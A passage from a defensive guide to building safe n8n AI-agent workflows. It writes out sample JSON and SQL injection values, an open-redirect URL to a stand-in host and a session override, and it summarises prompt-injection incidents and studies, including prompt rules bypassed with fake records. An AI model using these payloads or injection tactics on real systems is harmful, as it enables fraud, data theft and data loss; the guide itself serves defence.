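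If the HTTP Request node's list of allowed domains contained a wildcard such as `*.example.com`, the node could send a credential to unintended domains. n8n fixed this in version 1.121.0, and GCVE's *GHSA-2XCX-75H9-VR9H* (2026) recommends that users who can't upgrade yet list the domains individually. In another flaw, an expression could read the key from the request's headers while the node fetched results page by page, and copy it into the workflow's data. A later HTTP Request node could then send the key anywhere. GitLab's *CVE-2026-59209* (2026) explains that the domain restriction didn't apply because the key was by then ordinary data.

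All of these attacks require an account on the installation. They still matter to a builder who relies on the restriction to contain a wrong value from the model, because the restriction works only in nodes that enforce it. In another flaw, n8n checked a user's permission for a credential against the text of an expression, but then loaded the credential that the expression produced, according to GitLab's *GHSA-6qc9-mqvw-jg7x* (2026). A check on a model-filled URL can fail in the same way if it uses the template in the field instead of the finished address.

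### Redirects

A request can also end up at a host that neither the builder nor the model chose. A redirect is a response that refers the sender to a different address, and n8n's HTTP Request node follows redirects by default. Suppose `refunds.example` has a page that forwards visitors to any address in its `to` parameter. A model that can write the path and query could use it to leave the allowed domain:

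`https://refunds.example/go?to=https://collect.example`

Some redirects make the sender repeat the method and body at the new address, so the order number and amount would arrive there too. Whether the key is also sent depends on the software. Tines removes the Authorization header when a redirect leads to a different host, unless the user chooses otherwise, according to Tines' *Redirect authorization in HTTP Request Action*. Keys in other headers are more likely to be sent on. follow-redirects, a programming library for Node.js, lets developers list further headers to leave out, such as `X-API-Key`, but the list is empty by default.

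n8n also runs on Node.js, but its page on the HTTP Request node doesn't cover which headers survive a redirect, and its description of the domain restriction doesn't mention redirects at all. The shop can avoid the question by turning redirects off in the refund tool, since a refund service has little reason to use them. Lowering the maximum number wouldn't achieve the same thing, because one redirect is enough. SSRF protection doesn't solve this either. It checks where a redirect leads, but only to keep n8n away from blocked addresses, and `collect.example` is a public host.

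### Three ways to build the refund body

Suppose the shop now looks up the order before the agent starts and copies the order id and amount from the database into the refund request. The refund service also requires a reason, which the model writes. The model seems to have no control over the money any more, since it fills in only this one line of text.

The builder could write the body as JSON and splice the reason into it:

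```
{
  "order_id": {{ $json.order_id }},
  "amount": {{ $json.amount }},
  "reason": "{{ $fromAI("reason", "Why the customer wants a refund") }}"
}
```

Customer 417 bought a 12-inch lamp, and the model writes `12" lamp arrived broken`. The body becomes:

`{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80, "reason": "12" lamp arrived broken" }`

In JSON, the second quotation mark ends the text, so the reason becomes "12" and the program reading the body can't parse the words after it. The mark is correct in ordinary writing, but here it makes the request fail. The failure is visible, so the builder will probably notice it quickly.

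A silent one is possible too. If injected text makes the model return `broken", "amount": 8000, "x": "`, the result is valid JSON:

`{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80, "reason": "broken", "amount": 8000, "x": "" }`

The body now contains two amounts. Most programs that read JSON, including JavaScript's own parser, keep the last one, so the refund service receives a request for 8,000 euros even though the expression correctly copied 80 euros from the database. A builder who has to write the body as JSON can prevent this by using `{{ JSON.stringify($fromAI("reason")) }}` without quotation marks around it. `JSON.stringify` adds the quotation marks itself and marks any inside the text as ordinary characters, much as URL encoding does for a slash.

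The second way is to choose the option Using Fields Below and enter each name and value separately. The model fills in only the value named `reason`, and the node assembles the JSON afterwards:

`{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80, "reason": "12\" lamp arrived broken" }`

The backslash marks the quotation mark as part of the text, so the injected value would also end up in the reason, where it looks odd but leaves the amount at 80. This applies binding to a web request, and it's the best of the three for a refund. It doesn't ensure that the values are correct, because if the model still filled in the order id, it could enter 8813.

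Separate fields have a drawback that may lead builders to return to splicing. When n8n imports a request from an example in a service's documentation, it turns every parameter value into a string, so a service that requires a number may reject `"80"`. In that case, n8n advises switching to the JSON option, which is safe with fixed values but not when a model's text is inserted between quotation marks.

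(Other body formats have the same choice. A form body can be a single line such as `order_id=8812&amount=80&reason=broken`, where an ampersand in the reason starts a new parameter, or a set of separate fields.)

The third way is to let the model write the whole body:

`{{ $fromAI("body", "The refund request", "json") }}`

The quotation mark is no longer a problem, because n8n receives a finished JSON object and doesn't insert it into other text. But the model again controls the order id and the amount, and it can add keys that the builder never mentioned:

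`{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80, "reason": "broken", "destination": "account 5590" }`

n8n accepts this, since the type json allows any key. The refund service might reject the unknown key or ignore it. If it has an optional `destination` field for customers whose cards have expired, it pays 80 euros into account 5590. The order and the amount are both correct, so comparing them with the database would reveal nothing. To know what the model can do with this tool, the builder would have to know every optional field that the service accepts, including those it adds next year. Tenable's travel agent had a similar weakness, because its update action could change every field of a booking.

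Letting the model write the whole request body can be reasonable when the service only searches. In *“Received tool input did not match expected schema” when calling HTTP tool*, a user built such a tool for the search service exa.ai. An extra key in the body might change the search results, but it wouldn't move any money.

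## Database fields: statements, values, table names and filters

A database node gives the builder much the same choices as a request body. The model can supply a value or write the whole SQL statement, and n8n can insert the value into the statement or pass it separately. But a single SQL statement can change every row of a table.

Suppose the shop adds a Postgres tool for changing delivery addresses. Customer 417 has moved and asks the shop to send order 8813 to 4 Rue d'Alsace, Lyon. The database should end up running this statement:

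`UPDATE orders SET address = '4 Rue d''Alsace, Lyon' WHERE id = 8813`

In SQL, text stands between single quotation marks, so an apostrophe inside the text has to appear twice.

### One address change, built in four ways

The builder can let the model write the whole SQL statement by choosing the Execute Query operation and putting only `{{ $fromAI("query") }}` in the Query field. If the model writes an `UPDATE` to change one order's address but leaves out `WHERE id = 8813`, all 10,000 orders get the same address. The model can also write a `DELETE` or read a table of employees, because nothing in the node limits the statement.

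In the n8n forum thread *Running sql query by AI into postgres*, davidjm used a model node to turn questions about products into SQL and asked how to pass the result to the Postgres node. A reply suggested putting `{{ $json.text }}` in the Query field, and it worked. Only a line in the model's prompt prohibited inserts, updates and deletions, so if the model had written a deletion, the node would have run it.

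A second way is to write the statement by hand and splice in the two values:

`UPDATE orders SET address = '{{ $fromAI("address") }}' WHERE id = {{ $fromAI("order_id", "Order number", "number") }}`

With the correct address this fails, because the apostrophe in "d'Alsace" ends the text early and PostgreSQL can't parse the rest. A hostile value does more. If the model returns `Lyon', price = 0 --` as the address, the database receives:

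`UPDATE orders SET address = 'Lyon', price = 0 --' WHERE id = 8813`

Two hyphens start a comment in SQL, so PostgreSQL ignores the condition at the end. Every order now goes to Lyon and costs nothing. This is SQL injection, in which a database interprets part of an input as a command. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026) argue in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* that a model usually gives an attacker a way to reach an existing weakness rather than creating a new one. In the shop's tool, the weakness is the text field that the builder spliced into the SQL command. The order id can't be used this way because n8n accepts only a number there.

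PostgreSQL also accepts several statements in one query, separated by semicolons, so a value spliced into an `UPDATE` could add a `DELETE` after it. A spliced value can therefore do nearly as much damage as a statement the model writes itself. However, the value would have to be much more unusual, whereas a model that writes the whole statement can do the damage if it simply omits the `WHERE` condition.

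The third way is binding:

`UPDATE orders SET address = $1 WHERE id = $2`

The two values go into the Query Parameters field as `{{ [ $fromAI("address"), $fromAI("order_id") ] }}`. In a prepared statement, the database parses the text with its placeholders first and receives the values afterwards. The statement's table, columns and condition are fixed by then, so the hostile address from before would only be stored as the address text on order 8813.

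n8n's documentation calls these prepared statements, but the current node probably works a little differently. Its code uses pg-promise, a library that normally puts each value between quotation marks, doubles any apostrophes inside it and inserts the result before the query leaves n8n. The builder gets the same protection as long as the library quotes correctly.

Finally, the builder can choose the Update operation, pick the table and columns from a list, and let the model fill in only the two values. n8n then writes the statement. The tests in *fix(Postgres Node)*, a change to n8n's code (michael-radency and dana-gill, 2025), show that the node's fixed operations treat the condition value `select 2` as text to compare with, and that n8n passes columns and values separately from the statement.

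| How the builder sets up the tool | What one call can change |
|---|---|
| Model writes the statement | anything the database role permits |
| Spliced values | nearly the same, given a suitable value |
| Bound values | the address of any one of 10,000 orders |
| Update operation, two open values | the address of any one of 10,000 orders |
| Bound values plus a fixed customer number | the address of order 8812 or 8813 |

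Binding doesn't check whose order it is. If the model returns 2031, the statement changes the address on another customer's order, and that customer's parcel goes to Lyon. For the narrower reach in the last row, the workflow has to look up the customer number before the agent runs, and the builder adds it as a third condition that the model can't fill:

`UPDATE orders SET address = $1 WHERE id = $2 AND customer_id = $3 RETURNING id`

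If the model now returns 2031, no row matches. PostgreSQL doesn't treat this as an error, so without `RETURNING id` the agent might tell customer 417 that the address has changed. `RETURNING id` makes the database return the order number of each changed row, so an empty result shows that nothing changed. The customer number is only as reliable as the lookup that supplies it. If the workflow finds it from the sender's address, someone who forges that address gets customer 417's two orders.

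The Update operation can also change columns the builder didn't intend to change. In Map Automatically mode, n8n matches the field names in the incoming data to the table's columns. In a workflow without an agent, a model node might produce `{ "id": 8813, "address": "4 Rue d'Alsace, Lyon", "price": 0 }`. The database node would then set the price to 0, even though the builder meant to update only the address. Mapping each column manually avoids this.

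### Table names

A placeholder such as `$1` can stand for a value but not for the name of a table or column, because PostgreSQL can't prepare a statement until the table it concerns is specified. A reply in *Using the IN clause with CUSTOM PostgreSQL query*, a thread on the forum of the web development tool Wappler, quotes the statement in node-postgres's documentation that PostgreSQL doesn't support parameters for identifiers.

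n8n handles names with a second kind of placeholder. Its example is this query, with `users` as the first parameter and an email address as the second:

`SELECT * FROM $1:name WHERE email = $2`

The `:name` suffix makes n8n quote the value as a name. If a model returned `users; DROP TABLE orders`, PostgreSQL would treat the whole string as one table name and return an error because no such table exists.

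Quoting doesn't stop the model from filling in a valid but wrong table name, such as `employees`. Suppose the shop's builder writes `UPDATE $1:name SET address = $2 WHERE id = $3` so that one tool can serve both orders and returns. If the model fills in `suppliers`, and a supplier with the number 8813 exists, the query overwrites that supplier's address, and the shop's next payment reminder to the supplier goes to a flat in Lyon. This happens even though the statement is well formed and the quoting is correct. The model in the forum thread about inserting data chose "employees" in the same way, with no attack involved.

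Two tools, each with a fixed table, would be safer than one tool that lets the model fill in the table name. Fixing the column names would also be safer, since `price` and `address` are both valid even when the model picks the wrong one.

An expression inside the query can avoid dangerous splicing by producing only placeholders. n8n's *Common issues* shows how to do this when searching for a list of values with SQL's `IN`. The expression produces one placeholder per item, such as `$1, $2, $3`, and the values go into Query Parameters. The shop could use this to look up several orders at once. An empty list would produce `IN ()`, which PostgreSQL rejects. Binding each value doesn't limit how many rows a call affects, so an update with a long list could change any group of orders.

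### Commas, gaps and the order of placeholders

The Query Parameters field has a trap of its own. n8n describes its content as a comma-separated list, so a builder might reasonably write this:

`{{ $fromAI("address") }}, {{ $json.order_id }}`

The order id now comes from an earlier lookup, and the model fills in only the address. But Italian addresses often have a comma before the house number. For a customer who lives at Via Roma, 12, the finished list is `Via Roma, 12, 8813`. If n8n splits the list at every comma, the first placeholder gets "Via Roma" and the second gets 12, so the statement changes the address of order 12 instead of order 8813, the id the builder had fixed. The builder has in effect spliced the address into a list, where a comma causes the same problem as the quotation mark did in the SQL text. An attacker could choose which order to change by choosing the number after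 the comma.

In *Query Parameters*, miguelraatz reports that the MySQL node on n8n 1.26.0 split a company name at its comma, putting the first part in one placeholder and the second part in the next. On 1.56.2, the node saved only the text before the comma and gave no error, according to *MySQL Node doesn't work for Parameritized Queries when there are commas*.

In *Postgres Query Parameters ... bug?*, jamescv traced the fault to version 2.5 of the Postgres node on n8n 1.53.1 and found that version 2.4 handled the same data correctly. Others confirmed the fault on n8n 1.67.1 and 1.72.1, and according to the last post it was gone in 1.81.4. The fault may be older than version 2.5 of the node, because someone replying to strongbow in *Postgres node* suspected the same cause on n8n 1.38.2. None of these threads covers n8n's current 2.x releases.

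Empty values caused a related fault. In *Postgres Query Parameters not liking null or empty parameters*, EricSGS found that n8n 1.68.0 dropped an empty value from the list, which left it too short. n8n then stopped with an error, which is better than continuing with the wrong values. That could happen if an extra comma offset the missing value, because the list would then have the right length.

EricSGS also found the remedy, which is to give the field a single expression that returns an array:

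`{{ [ $fromAI("address"), $json.order_id ] }}`

An array keeps each value separate, whatever characters it contains. Builders should use this form on every version, since it takes no extra work and n8n now uses it in its own example. One reply to miguelraatz instead replaced the commas with underscores, which lets the query run but stores the wrong company name.

A more recent thread reports trouble with the placeholders themselves. abc, in *Random and unexpected query parameter behavior*, ran a query with `$3`, `$2` and `$1` in that order and got the first, second and third values back. The replies explained that n8n fills placeholders in the order in which they appear and ignores their numbers. That fits this test but not abc's other one, where `$1`, `$2` and `$1` returned the first value twice and then the second, so the cause is still unclear. The consequences could be serious. Take a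 tool that changes quantities:

`UPDATE orders SET quantity = $2 WHERE id = $1`

With the values 8813 and 2, a node that ignored the placeholder numbers would set the quantity of order 2 to 8813. Using each placeholder once and in ascending order avoids the problem whether or not the node ignores the numbers.

The replies to abc recommended putting expressions straight into the query, and *N8n Gotchas*, another forum post, advises against using query parameters at all. It recommends building the complete SQL text in a Code node, with a small hand-written function that doubles the apostrophes. That can work, but forgetting to call the function even once makes the workflow vulnerable to SQL injection again, though it otherwise runs without errors.

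### Deleting with an empty filter

n8n's Delete operation has three commands. Truncate empties a table, Drop removes the table itself, and Delete removes the rows that match a condition under Select Rows. If the builder sets no condition, n8n warns, the command deletes all rows.

Other platforms have made the same choice. Workato's *IBM Db2* contains the same warning about a blank condition. SnapLogic's *PostgreSQL* describes a step in which the whole condition is one text field that an earlier step can supply. If that earlier step were a model, an empty answer would clear the table. In KNIME, a data analysis platform, the user instead has to choose between "Matching rows" and "All rows", so emptying a table is deliberate.

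n8n falls between these designs. The builder adds a condition with a column, an operator and a value, and the model typically fills in only the value. Suppose the shop has a tool that deletes a customer's abandoned orders by email address, and the model returns an empty string. The condition doesn't disappear. According to the tests by michael-radency and dana-gill, n8n adds the column and the value to the statement as a pair, which would give:

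`DELETE FROM orders WHERE email = ''`

If the email filter is bound to an empty string, the statement deletes only orders whose email field is blank. Dirask's *Node.js*, a short programming tutorial, runs a deletion like this and gets the same result. With a numeric column the statement should fail, because an empty string isn't a number. In *Postgres Node*, another thread on n8n's forum, PostgreSQL returned a similar error for a boolean column.

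With other operators, an empty value is much more dangerous:

| Condition, with an empty value from the model | Likely effect in a table of 10,000 orders |
|---|---|
| `email` equals the value | deletes orders with a blank email |
| `id` equals the value | error, nothing deleted |
| `email` differs from the value | deletes every order that has an email |
| `email` is like `%` + value + `%` | deletes every order that has an email |
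| `id` is at least the value | may delete every order |

In the fourth row, the percent signs stand for any text, so the pattern `%%` matches everything. The result in the last row depends on how n8n converts the value. For a condition with `>=`, n8n stops with an error if the value isn't a number, as one user found with a date. JavaScript's usual conversion turns an empty string into 0. If n8n uses that conversion, the empty value passes the check and the condition becomes `id >= 0`, which matches every order.

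n8n doesn't document what happens with an empty value, and the published tests don't cover it, so a builder should try it on a copy of the table. A deletion tool is safest with "equals" as a fixed operator and a numeric id as the only open field. If the model fills in the operator too, the condition "`id` differs from 8813" deletes 9,999 orders and spares the one that the customer asked about.

### The advisories of June and July 2026

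n8n had four SQL injection flaws of its own in the summer of 2026. Outside data can exploit two of them, while the other two need someone with an account.

GitLab's *GHSA-652q-gvq3-74qv* (2026) covers the node for Snowflake, a cloud database, whose Execute Query operation put the values of expressions directly into the SQL text. GitLab's *CVE-2026-59257* (2026) describes the same fault in the first version of the MySQL node, which n8n keeps for older workflows, but the current version doesn't have it. In both cases, the fault is exploitable only if a builder has put an expression containing untrusted data in a raw query. If an outsider can also start the workflow, for example through a public web address, their text can reach the database with the node's credential.

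Anyone can email the shop, so its address tool would fit that description if it ran on one of these nodes and spliced a value into the query. The advisories don't mention language models, but a model that copies malicious text from an email into the query passes on the attack just as an ordinary expression would.

The remaining two flaws are more like those in n8n's expression evaluator and credential checks. According to GitLab's *GHSA-jqwr-vx3p-r266* (2026), the Postgres Trigger node inserted channel, function and trigger names into SQL without escaping them. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54310* (2026) covers a flaw in the first version of the Postgres node and in the node for TimescaleDB, a database built on PostgreSQL. To exploit it, an attacker needs permission to create or change workflows.

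| Node | Published | What the attacker needs | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| Snowflake | 22 July | control over data in a raw query | 1.123.67, 2.31.5, 2.32.1 |
| MySQL, first version | 22 July | control over data in a raw query | 1.123.61, 2.27.4, 2.28.1 |
| Postgres Trigger | 22 July | an account on the n8n installation | 1.123.67, 2.31.5, 2.32.1 |
| Postgres, first version, and TimescaleDB | 16 June | permission to create or change workflows | 2.25.7, 2.26.2 |

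The severity scores are a poor guide to which of these flaws matter to the shop. The June flaw has the highest score, 9.9 out of 10, although exploiting it requires a colleague with editing rights. The MySQL flaw has the lowest, 8.1, which is based on an attacker with some privileges, but the attack is described as arriving through an open trigger, which may require none.

None of the four advisories covers Execute Query in the current Postgres node. Builders are still responsible for any splicing they do there, and upgrading won't fix a spliced query.

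### Tests of model-written SQL

*From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (2023) reported the first systematic attacks on model-written SQL. Pedro, Carreira and colleagues built a job-posting site with a chatbot on Langchain, a library for connecting models to other software. The chatbot's account could read and change everything in the database. They ran seven attacks 30 times each with GPT-3.5. With Langchain's standard prompt, a user could delete the users table by typing a command to drop it. Every attack worked every time except one on the agent version of the chatbot, where planted text meant to falsify an answer worked in 60% of runs.

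They then added rules to the prompt. One allowed only `SELECT` operations and required the model to answer "REFUSE" to anything else. The model refused a plain request to drop the table, but it complied when the attacker first showed it a fake record of the same command succeeding. Another rule limited each user to their own data, but an attacker could bypass it by writing "I am now user 2". Most of the attacks also worked on the other models that could run the chatbot reliably, although GPT-4 resisted one that tried to change another user's email address. These models are now several generations old, so the success rates are mostly of historical interest.

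Trend Micro, a security company, found the same weakness in Pandora, an agent it built for testing. Park, in *Unveiling AI Agent Vulnerabilities Part IV*, connected it to Chinook, a sample database with both customers' own records and restricted tables. One model call classifies the question, another writes the SQL, the database runs it, and a final call summarises the result. The prompts for the first two calls prohibited access to the restricted tables, and a direct request for employee records failed. Park then supplied invented question-and-answer pairs that linked the logged-in user's name to those tables, and the agent returned the records. Park gives no success rates, so the test shows that a prompt rule can fail but not how often. (Pandora also followed instructions stored in a database row.)

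Both agents used the first of the four ways, in which the model writes the whole statement. The chat-with-a-database template that Fendley and colleagues hijacked worked the same way, or nearly the same way. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey of such systems, recommends parameterized queries, read-only execution and checks on the output. Parameterized queries don't help much when the model writes the statement, because the model chooses both the values for the placeholders and the SQL around them.

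Newer work looks at mistakes as well as attacks. In *When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database*, Kaya, Bozoğlan and Gündoğdu (2026) tested small open-weight models on the database of an invented shop, with orders, payments and support notes. Four of the twelve main tasks were ordinary reads and changes, and the other eight contained a hazard that the prompt didn't mention. For example, one asked the agent to free up space on a full disk, and another asked for a summary of support notes, one of which contained an instruction to delete cancelled orders. They marked every fiftieth row as protected and checked afterwards which of these rows were permanently lost or altered.

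They ran the tasks with two kinds of database account. One was the account from the vendor's quickstart guide, which in most of the databases can do anything. The other followed the vendor's advice on minimal permissions, so it could read and change rows but couldn't drop or truncate tables. These are the shares of trials with lasting damage, from 432 trials per cell:

| | PostgreSQL, full account | PostgreSQL, limited account | MySQL, full account | MySQL, limited account |
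|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any protected rows lost | 13.7% | 5.1% | 15.3% | 6.9% |
| Original rows lost | 4.9% | 4.9% | 7.2% | 6.7% |

The limited account's large advantage in the first row comes mostly from a backup copy of the orders table, which agents with a full account often dropped, sometimes because the task told them to remove everything not on a list. The second row excludes that copy and shows almost no difference between the accounts, because the limited account still allowed `DELETE` and `UPDATE`. On PostgreSQL, the planted support note caused 11 of the 21 losses of original rows with the full account.

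In the disk-space task on PostgreSQL, the database blocked the limited account from truncating or dropping a table. In 6 of 36 trials, the agent then deleted rows from the same table instead.

The models had 4 to 12 billion parameters, except for one larger model in which only a small part is active at a time, so the damage rates are weak evidence about the models a business would probably use. The researchers also added the measure for original rows after seeing their first results. Still, the explanation doesn't depend on the model, because any account with permission to delete rows can delete the wrong ones.

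### What a database role can stop

A prompt rule depends on the model following it, while PostgreSQL enforces a role's permissions on every statement. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) counts these access rights among the reasons why running SQL needs less isolation than running a general programming language. The shop could create a role for its address tool with these permissions:

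```sql
GRANT SELECT ON orders TO shop_agent;
GRANT UPDATE (address) ON orders TO shop_agent;
```

Even if the model wrote the whole statement, it couldn't change a price, delete an order or read the employees table. The spliced address with `price = 0` would fail too. The role would still allow the model to give all 10,000 orders the same address, because permission to update a column in PostgreSQL applies to every row in the table.

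A read-only database role suits the shop's original Postgres tool, which looks up orders. *AgentNLQ* (2026), a system that turns questions into SQL, blocks statements such as insert, update, delete and drop before they run. Role permissions are more reliable because they don't depend on recognising a dangerous statement from its text. Neither method prevents a query from exposing other customers' orders.

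Read access can do damage in other ways. *Data Agents Under Attack* (Wang, Wang et al., 2026) points out that a valid query can join large tables and use up the database's resources, and that the model can't easily estimate beforehand how much a query will use. In PostgreSQL, a `SELECT` can also call a function, and some functions run with their owner's permissions. If such a function cancels orders, a read-only role that is allowed to call it can cancel them.

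Wang and colleagues describe another case of the confused deputy, in which an agent often uses one shared account with broader rights than the person it works for. The shop's database role, for example, has to cover both customer 417 and customer 418.

Row-level security can close this gap. It attaches a rule to a table, and PostgreSQL then applies the rule to every query on it:

```sql
ALTER TABLE orders ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;
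CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders TO shop_agent
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer_id')::int);
```

If the workflow sets `app.customer_id` to 417, the role can read and change only orders 8812 and 8813. An update without any condition would affect two orders instead of 10,000. The rule doesn't apply to superusers or, normally, to the table's owner, so a node that logs in as either gets no protection.

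The setting is the weak point. It belongs to a database session, and two separate Postgres nodes may not share one, so the builder should set the customer number in the same query that uses it. A model that writes its own SQL can also change it:

`SET app.customer_id = '418'`

PostgreSQL allows any role to change a setting of this kind. A spliced value could therefore change it by adding a second statement, but a bound value could not. Row-level security in this form works well with binding or a fixed operation, where it catches a wrong order id. To contain a model that writes whole statements, the shop would need an identity that SQL can't change, such as a separate login for each customer.

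Limiting an agent's permissions also doesn't help if the agent finds the login for an account with more. Kaya and colleagues planted a superuser's password in a table, and agents with limited accounts read it and used it in 24 of 4,032 trials. In n8n, the builder sets the node's credential, so a model couldn't use the password to log in through the same tool, but it could still copy the password into an email.

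The shop needs a backup for the mistakes that a role allows. n8n can run several queries as one transaction and undo them all if one fails, but a wrong update that succeeds stays in the table. When Kaya and colleagues applied 21 scripted mistakes to PostgreSQL without a backup, 17 permanently destroyed protected rows, compared with none under the vendor's minimum backup setup. They had made the backup just before each mistake, with no real orders in between, so a working shop would have a harder time separating the wrong changes from a day's legitimate ones.

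## Messages and records that start further actions

The shop can correct a wrong row from a backup, but another program may already have read it and acted on it, even if the row held only a free-text note.

Text can cause a later action in four ways:

- The program that receives a message parses part of it as a command, a mention or a link.
- A new row or message triggers another workflow.
- A tool result contains instructions, and the agent that reads it makes another call in the same run.
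- A record or an agent's memory keeps the text until a later run reads it.

Attackers can use all of these for prompt injection, but honest text can set off further actions too.

### Messages that other programs parse

Many programs treat certain text they receive as commands, like the helpdesk that closes tickets marked "resolved". GitHub closes issue 12 when a developer merges a change whose description contains "fixes #12". Slack notifies the members of a channel if a workflow posts a message containing `<!channel>`. Google Sheets can treat text that starts with an equals sign as a formula, and some formulas fetch data from a web address.

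Some services let the sender prevent it. Google Sheets can store a value as plain text, and Slack shows the code as ordinary characters if the workflow first replaces `<` with `&lt;`.

A link in a message can trigger a web request before anyone clicks it. Many chat programs fetch the linked page to show a preview, and email programs may load images from other servers. If the model puts order numbers in such a URL, they can leak as soon as the message appears on a screen, much as they can through a tool that lets the model choose the URL.

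Researchers at the security company Noma showed a similar leak in Agentforce, Salesforce's product for agents that work with customer data. According to The Hacker News' *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025), they put instructions into the Description field of a public form for sales enquiries. SecurityWeek reports that when an employee asked the agent to process the enquiry, it collected customer data, which left the company in the parameters of a web request. Salesforce had also let one of its trusted domains expire, so an attacker could have registered it and received the data there. Salesforce has since recovered the domain and stopped agents from sending output to untrusted domains. A list of allowed domains in n8n also needs upkeep, because a domain on it may change owners.

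### Writes that trigger workflows

n8n's Postgres Trigger node can start a workflow when a row changes. Pipedream, another automation platform, has triggers for new and closed tickets in the helpdesk Zendesk and for updated requests in Jira, which tracks tasks. It also has actions that create tickets and comments, so what one workflow does can start the next.

A single message can start a chain of actions across several products. *When a Jira Ticket Can Steal Your Secrets* (Simon Willison, 2025) describes a demonstration by the security company Zenity Labs. Companies often connect Zendesk to Jira so that a support email automatically becomes a Jira ticket. In the demonstration, the coding agent Cursor read such a ticket, which contained hidden instructions to search the company's code for a secret key and send it to an outside website. The sender didn't need a Jira account, and the developer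 using Cursor didn't have to open the support inbox.

In the n8n templates that Tang and colleagues studied, two of the most common arrangements are a messaging node directly after a model (5.5% of the places where a model appears) and a storage node directly after a model (2.8%). The templates can't show how often another workflow then reads the message or record, because that connection runs through an inbox or a table rather than a line on the canvas.

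### A refund that begins as a note

Suppose the shop takes the refund tool away from the agent that reads customers' emails, to protect against prompt injection. One workflow now has a model summarise each email and writes the summary into the order's notes column. A second workflow starts when a note changes, and its agent can issue refunds but never reads email.

Customer 417 writes that the lamp from order 8812 arrived broken and that someone on the phone promised a refund of 160 euros. The first workflow stores this note:

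`Lamp arrived broken. Refund of 160 euros agreed by phone.`

The agent in the second workflow reads the note and calls its refund tool with `{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 160 }`, which is twice what the lamp cost.

| Step | What happens | Credential used |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The first workflow fetches the email | the shop's Gmail account |
| 2 | Its model writes the summary | a key for the model provider |
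| 3 | Its Postgres node stores the summary | a database role that can change only `notes` |
| 4 | The second workflow starts and receives the row | a database login that can read orders |
| 5 | Its agent decides on a refund of 160 euros | a key for the model provider |
| 6 | Its HTTP Request tool posts the refund | the refund service's key |

Customer 417 has none of these credentials, and each node uses its own credentials for their intended purpose. The database role in step 3 is about as narrow as a role can be, but the first workflow can still influence a payment because the role restricts which column the node can change without restricting the text it writes there.

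An employee who checks the first workflow will find little to criticise. It binds the summary as a value, takes the order number from a lookup, and cannot move money, so the worst result seems to be an odd note. The second workflow also looks safe because it reads only the shop's own table. If someone later questions the payment, the log will show a refund and a note that supports it. The mistake arises because the first workflow's builder treated the notes as content while the second's treated them as instructions, and a reviewer cannot see both uses on either canvas.

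The customer may be telling the truth about the phone call. The summary caused the damage by recording the customer's claim as an agreement. If the note had read "Customer says someone promised 160 euros", the second agent might have left the case to an employee, depending on the model.

To find such connections, the shop could list which workflows write to each column or inbox and which read from it. If a customer's text can end up in a column that an agent with a refund tool reads, the shop should treat that column as carefully as the email trigger.

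### Loops

Suppose the second workflow ends by writing "Refunded 160 euros" into the notes. The note has changed, so the workflow starts again. Even if the agent recognises that the refund is complete, recording "No action needed" starts another run. If the original note is still there, the agent may also issue the refund again. An idempotency key made from the order number would block the second refund but wouldn't stop the workflow from restarting.

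n8n's default limit of ten model runs per agent doesn't help, because it applies within one workflow run and each pass here is a new one. The same goes for an alarm recommended by TrendAI's *Pwning Agentic AI Part III*, part of a series that Trend Micro publishes under the name TrendAI. It goes off when a single task makes too many tool calls, and each pass through this loop makes only one or two.

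A status column can stop the loop. The first workflow sets it to "new" when it stores a summary, and the second runs this statement before the agent starts:

`UPDATE orders SET note_status = 'done' WHERE id = $1 AND note_status = 'new' RETURNING id`

If the statement returns nothing, another run has already taken the note, and the workflow ends. The update may trigger one more run, which finds no new note and stops. But if a run fails after this statement, customer 417 doesn't get a refund, so an employee has to check failed runs.

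An email loop requires two automatic responders, such as the shop's agent and a supplier's agent that both answer every email. The shop's agent thanks the supplier for its message, the supplier's agent thanks the shop, and the exchange continues. Automatic holiday replies usually avoid this by answering each sender only once every few days, but an agent has no such limit unless its builder adds one. A filter for identical messages would probably miss the loop, since a model rarely writes the same reply twice.

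Automatic emails can carry an `Auto-Submitted` header, which other programs can use to recognise them and not reply. The shop's workflow can check for this header before the agent runs. Some senders leave the header out, so it also helps to limit automatic replies, for example to three per address per day.

Longer loops can pass through several workflows. A counter stored with the record can end these loops if each workflow adds one to it and stops when the count exceeds a limit, such as five. Mail servers detect loops in a similar way, by counting the lines that each server adds to a message. The workflow has to update the counter through an expression, because a model might reset it.

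Almost 19% of the templates that Tang and colleagues examined contain a loop on the canvas. Many of these loops are probably deliberate, for example to process a list in batches. The figure doesn't include loops that run through a table or an inbox, because each workflow on its own may look like a straight line.

### The Supabase demonstration

The notes example needs two workflows, but a tool result can lead a single agent to make another call within the same run. In mid-2025, a team at General Analysis demonstrated this with Supabase, which provides PostgreSQL databases and a server that connects agents to them through the Model Context Protocol.

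*Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes a setup in which a customer files a support ticket that contains instructions, and a developer later asks Cursor to list the latest tickets. Pomerium's *When AI Has Root* explains that the customer can only create their own tickets and messages, and that support employees can answer tickets but can't open sensitive tables. The developer's agent, however, logs in with a role that bypasses row-level security.

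Cursor read the ticket and then ran two queries that the developer hadn't requested. One read a private table of tokens, which give access to other services, and the other inserted the tokens into the ticket as a new message. The customer could then see them by reloading the page. A support employee could have opened the same ticket safely, because their login didn't give access to the tokens.

On the discussion site Hacker News, a Supabase engineer replied that the company had added protections a few weeks earlier. Its server wrapped query results in text that discouraged the model from following instructions in them, and its documentation encouraged read-only access. The engineer wrote that the published attacks no longer worked after these changes, and complained that General Analysis hadn't followed Supabase's process for reporting flaws or answered its messages.

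Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) followed in September. Supabase said no customer had reported a leak of this kind, but acknowledged that the warnings had reduced the risk without eliminating it. Its main advice was never to connect an agent to production data. This suits a developer's coding tool, but the shop can't follow it because its agent needs customers' real orders to answer them.

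Willison points out that read-only access would have prevented this leak, since the agent couldn't have written the tokens into the ticket. Read-only access would not be enough for the shop, because its agent could still use the Gmail tool to send what it read.

### Authorised tools turned against their owner

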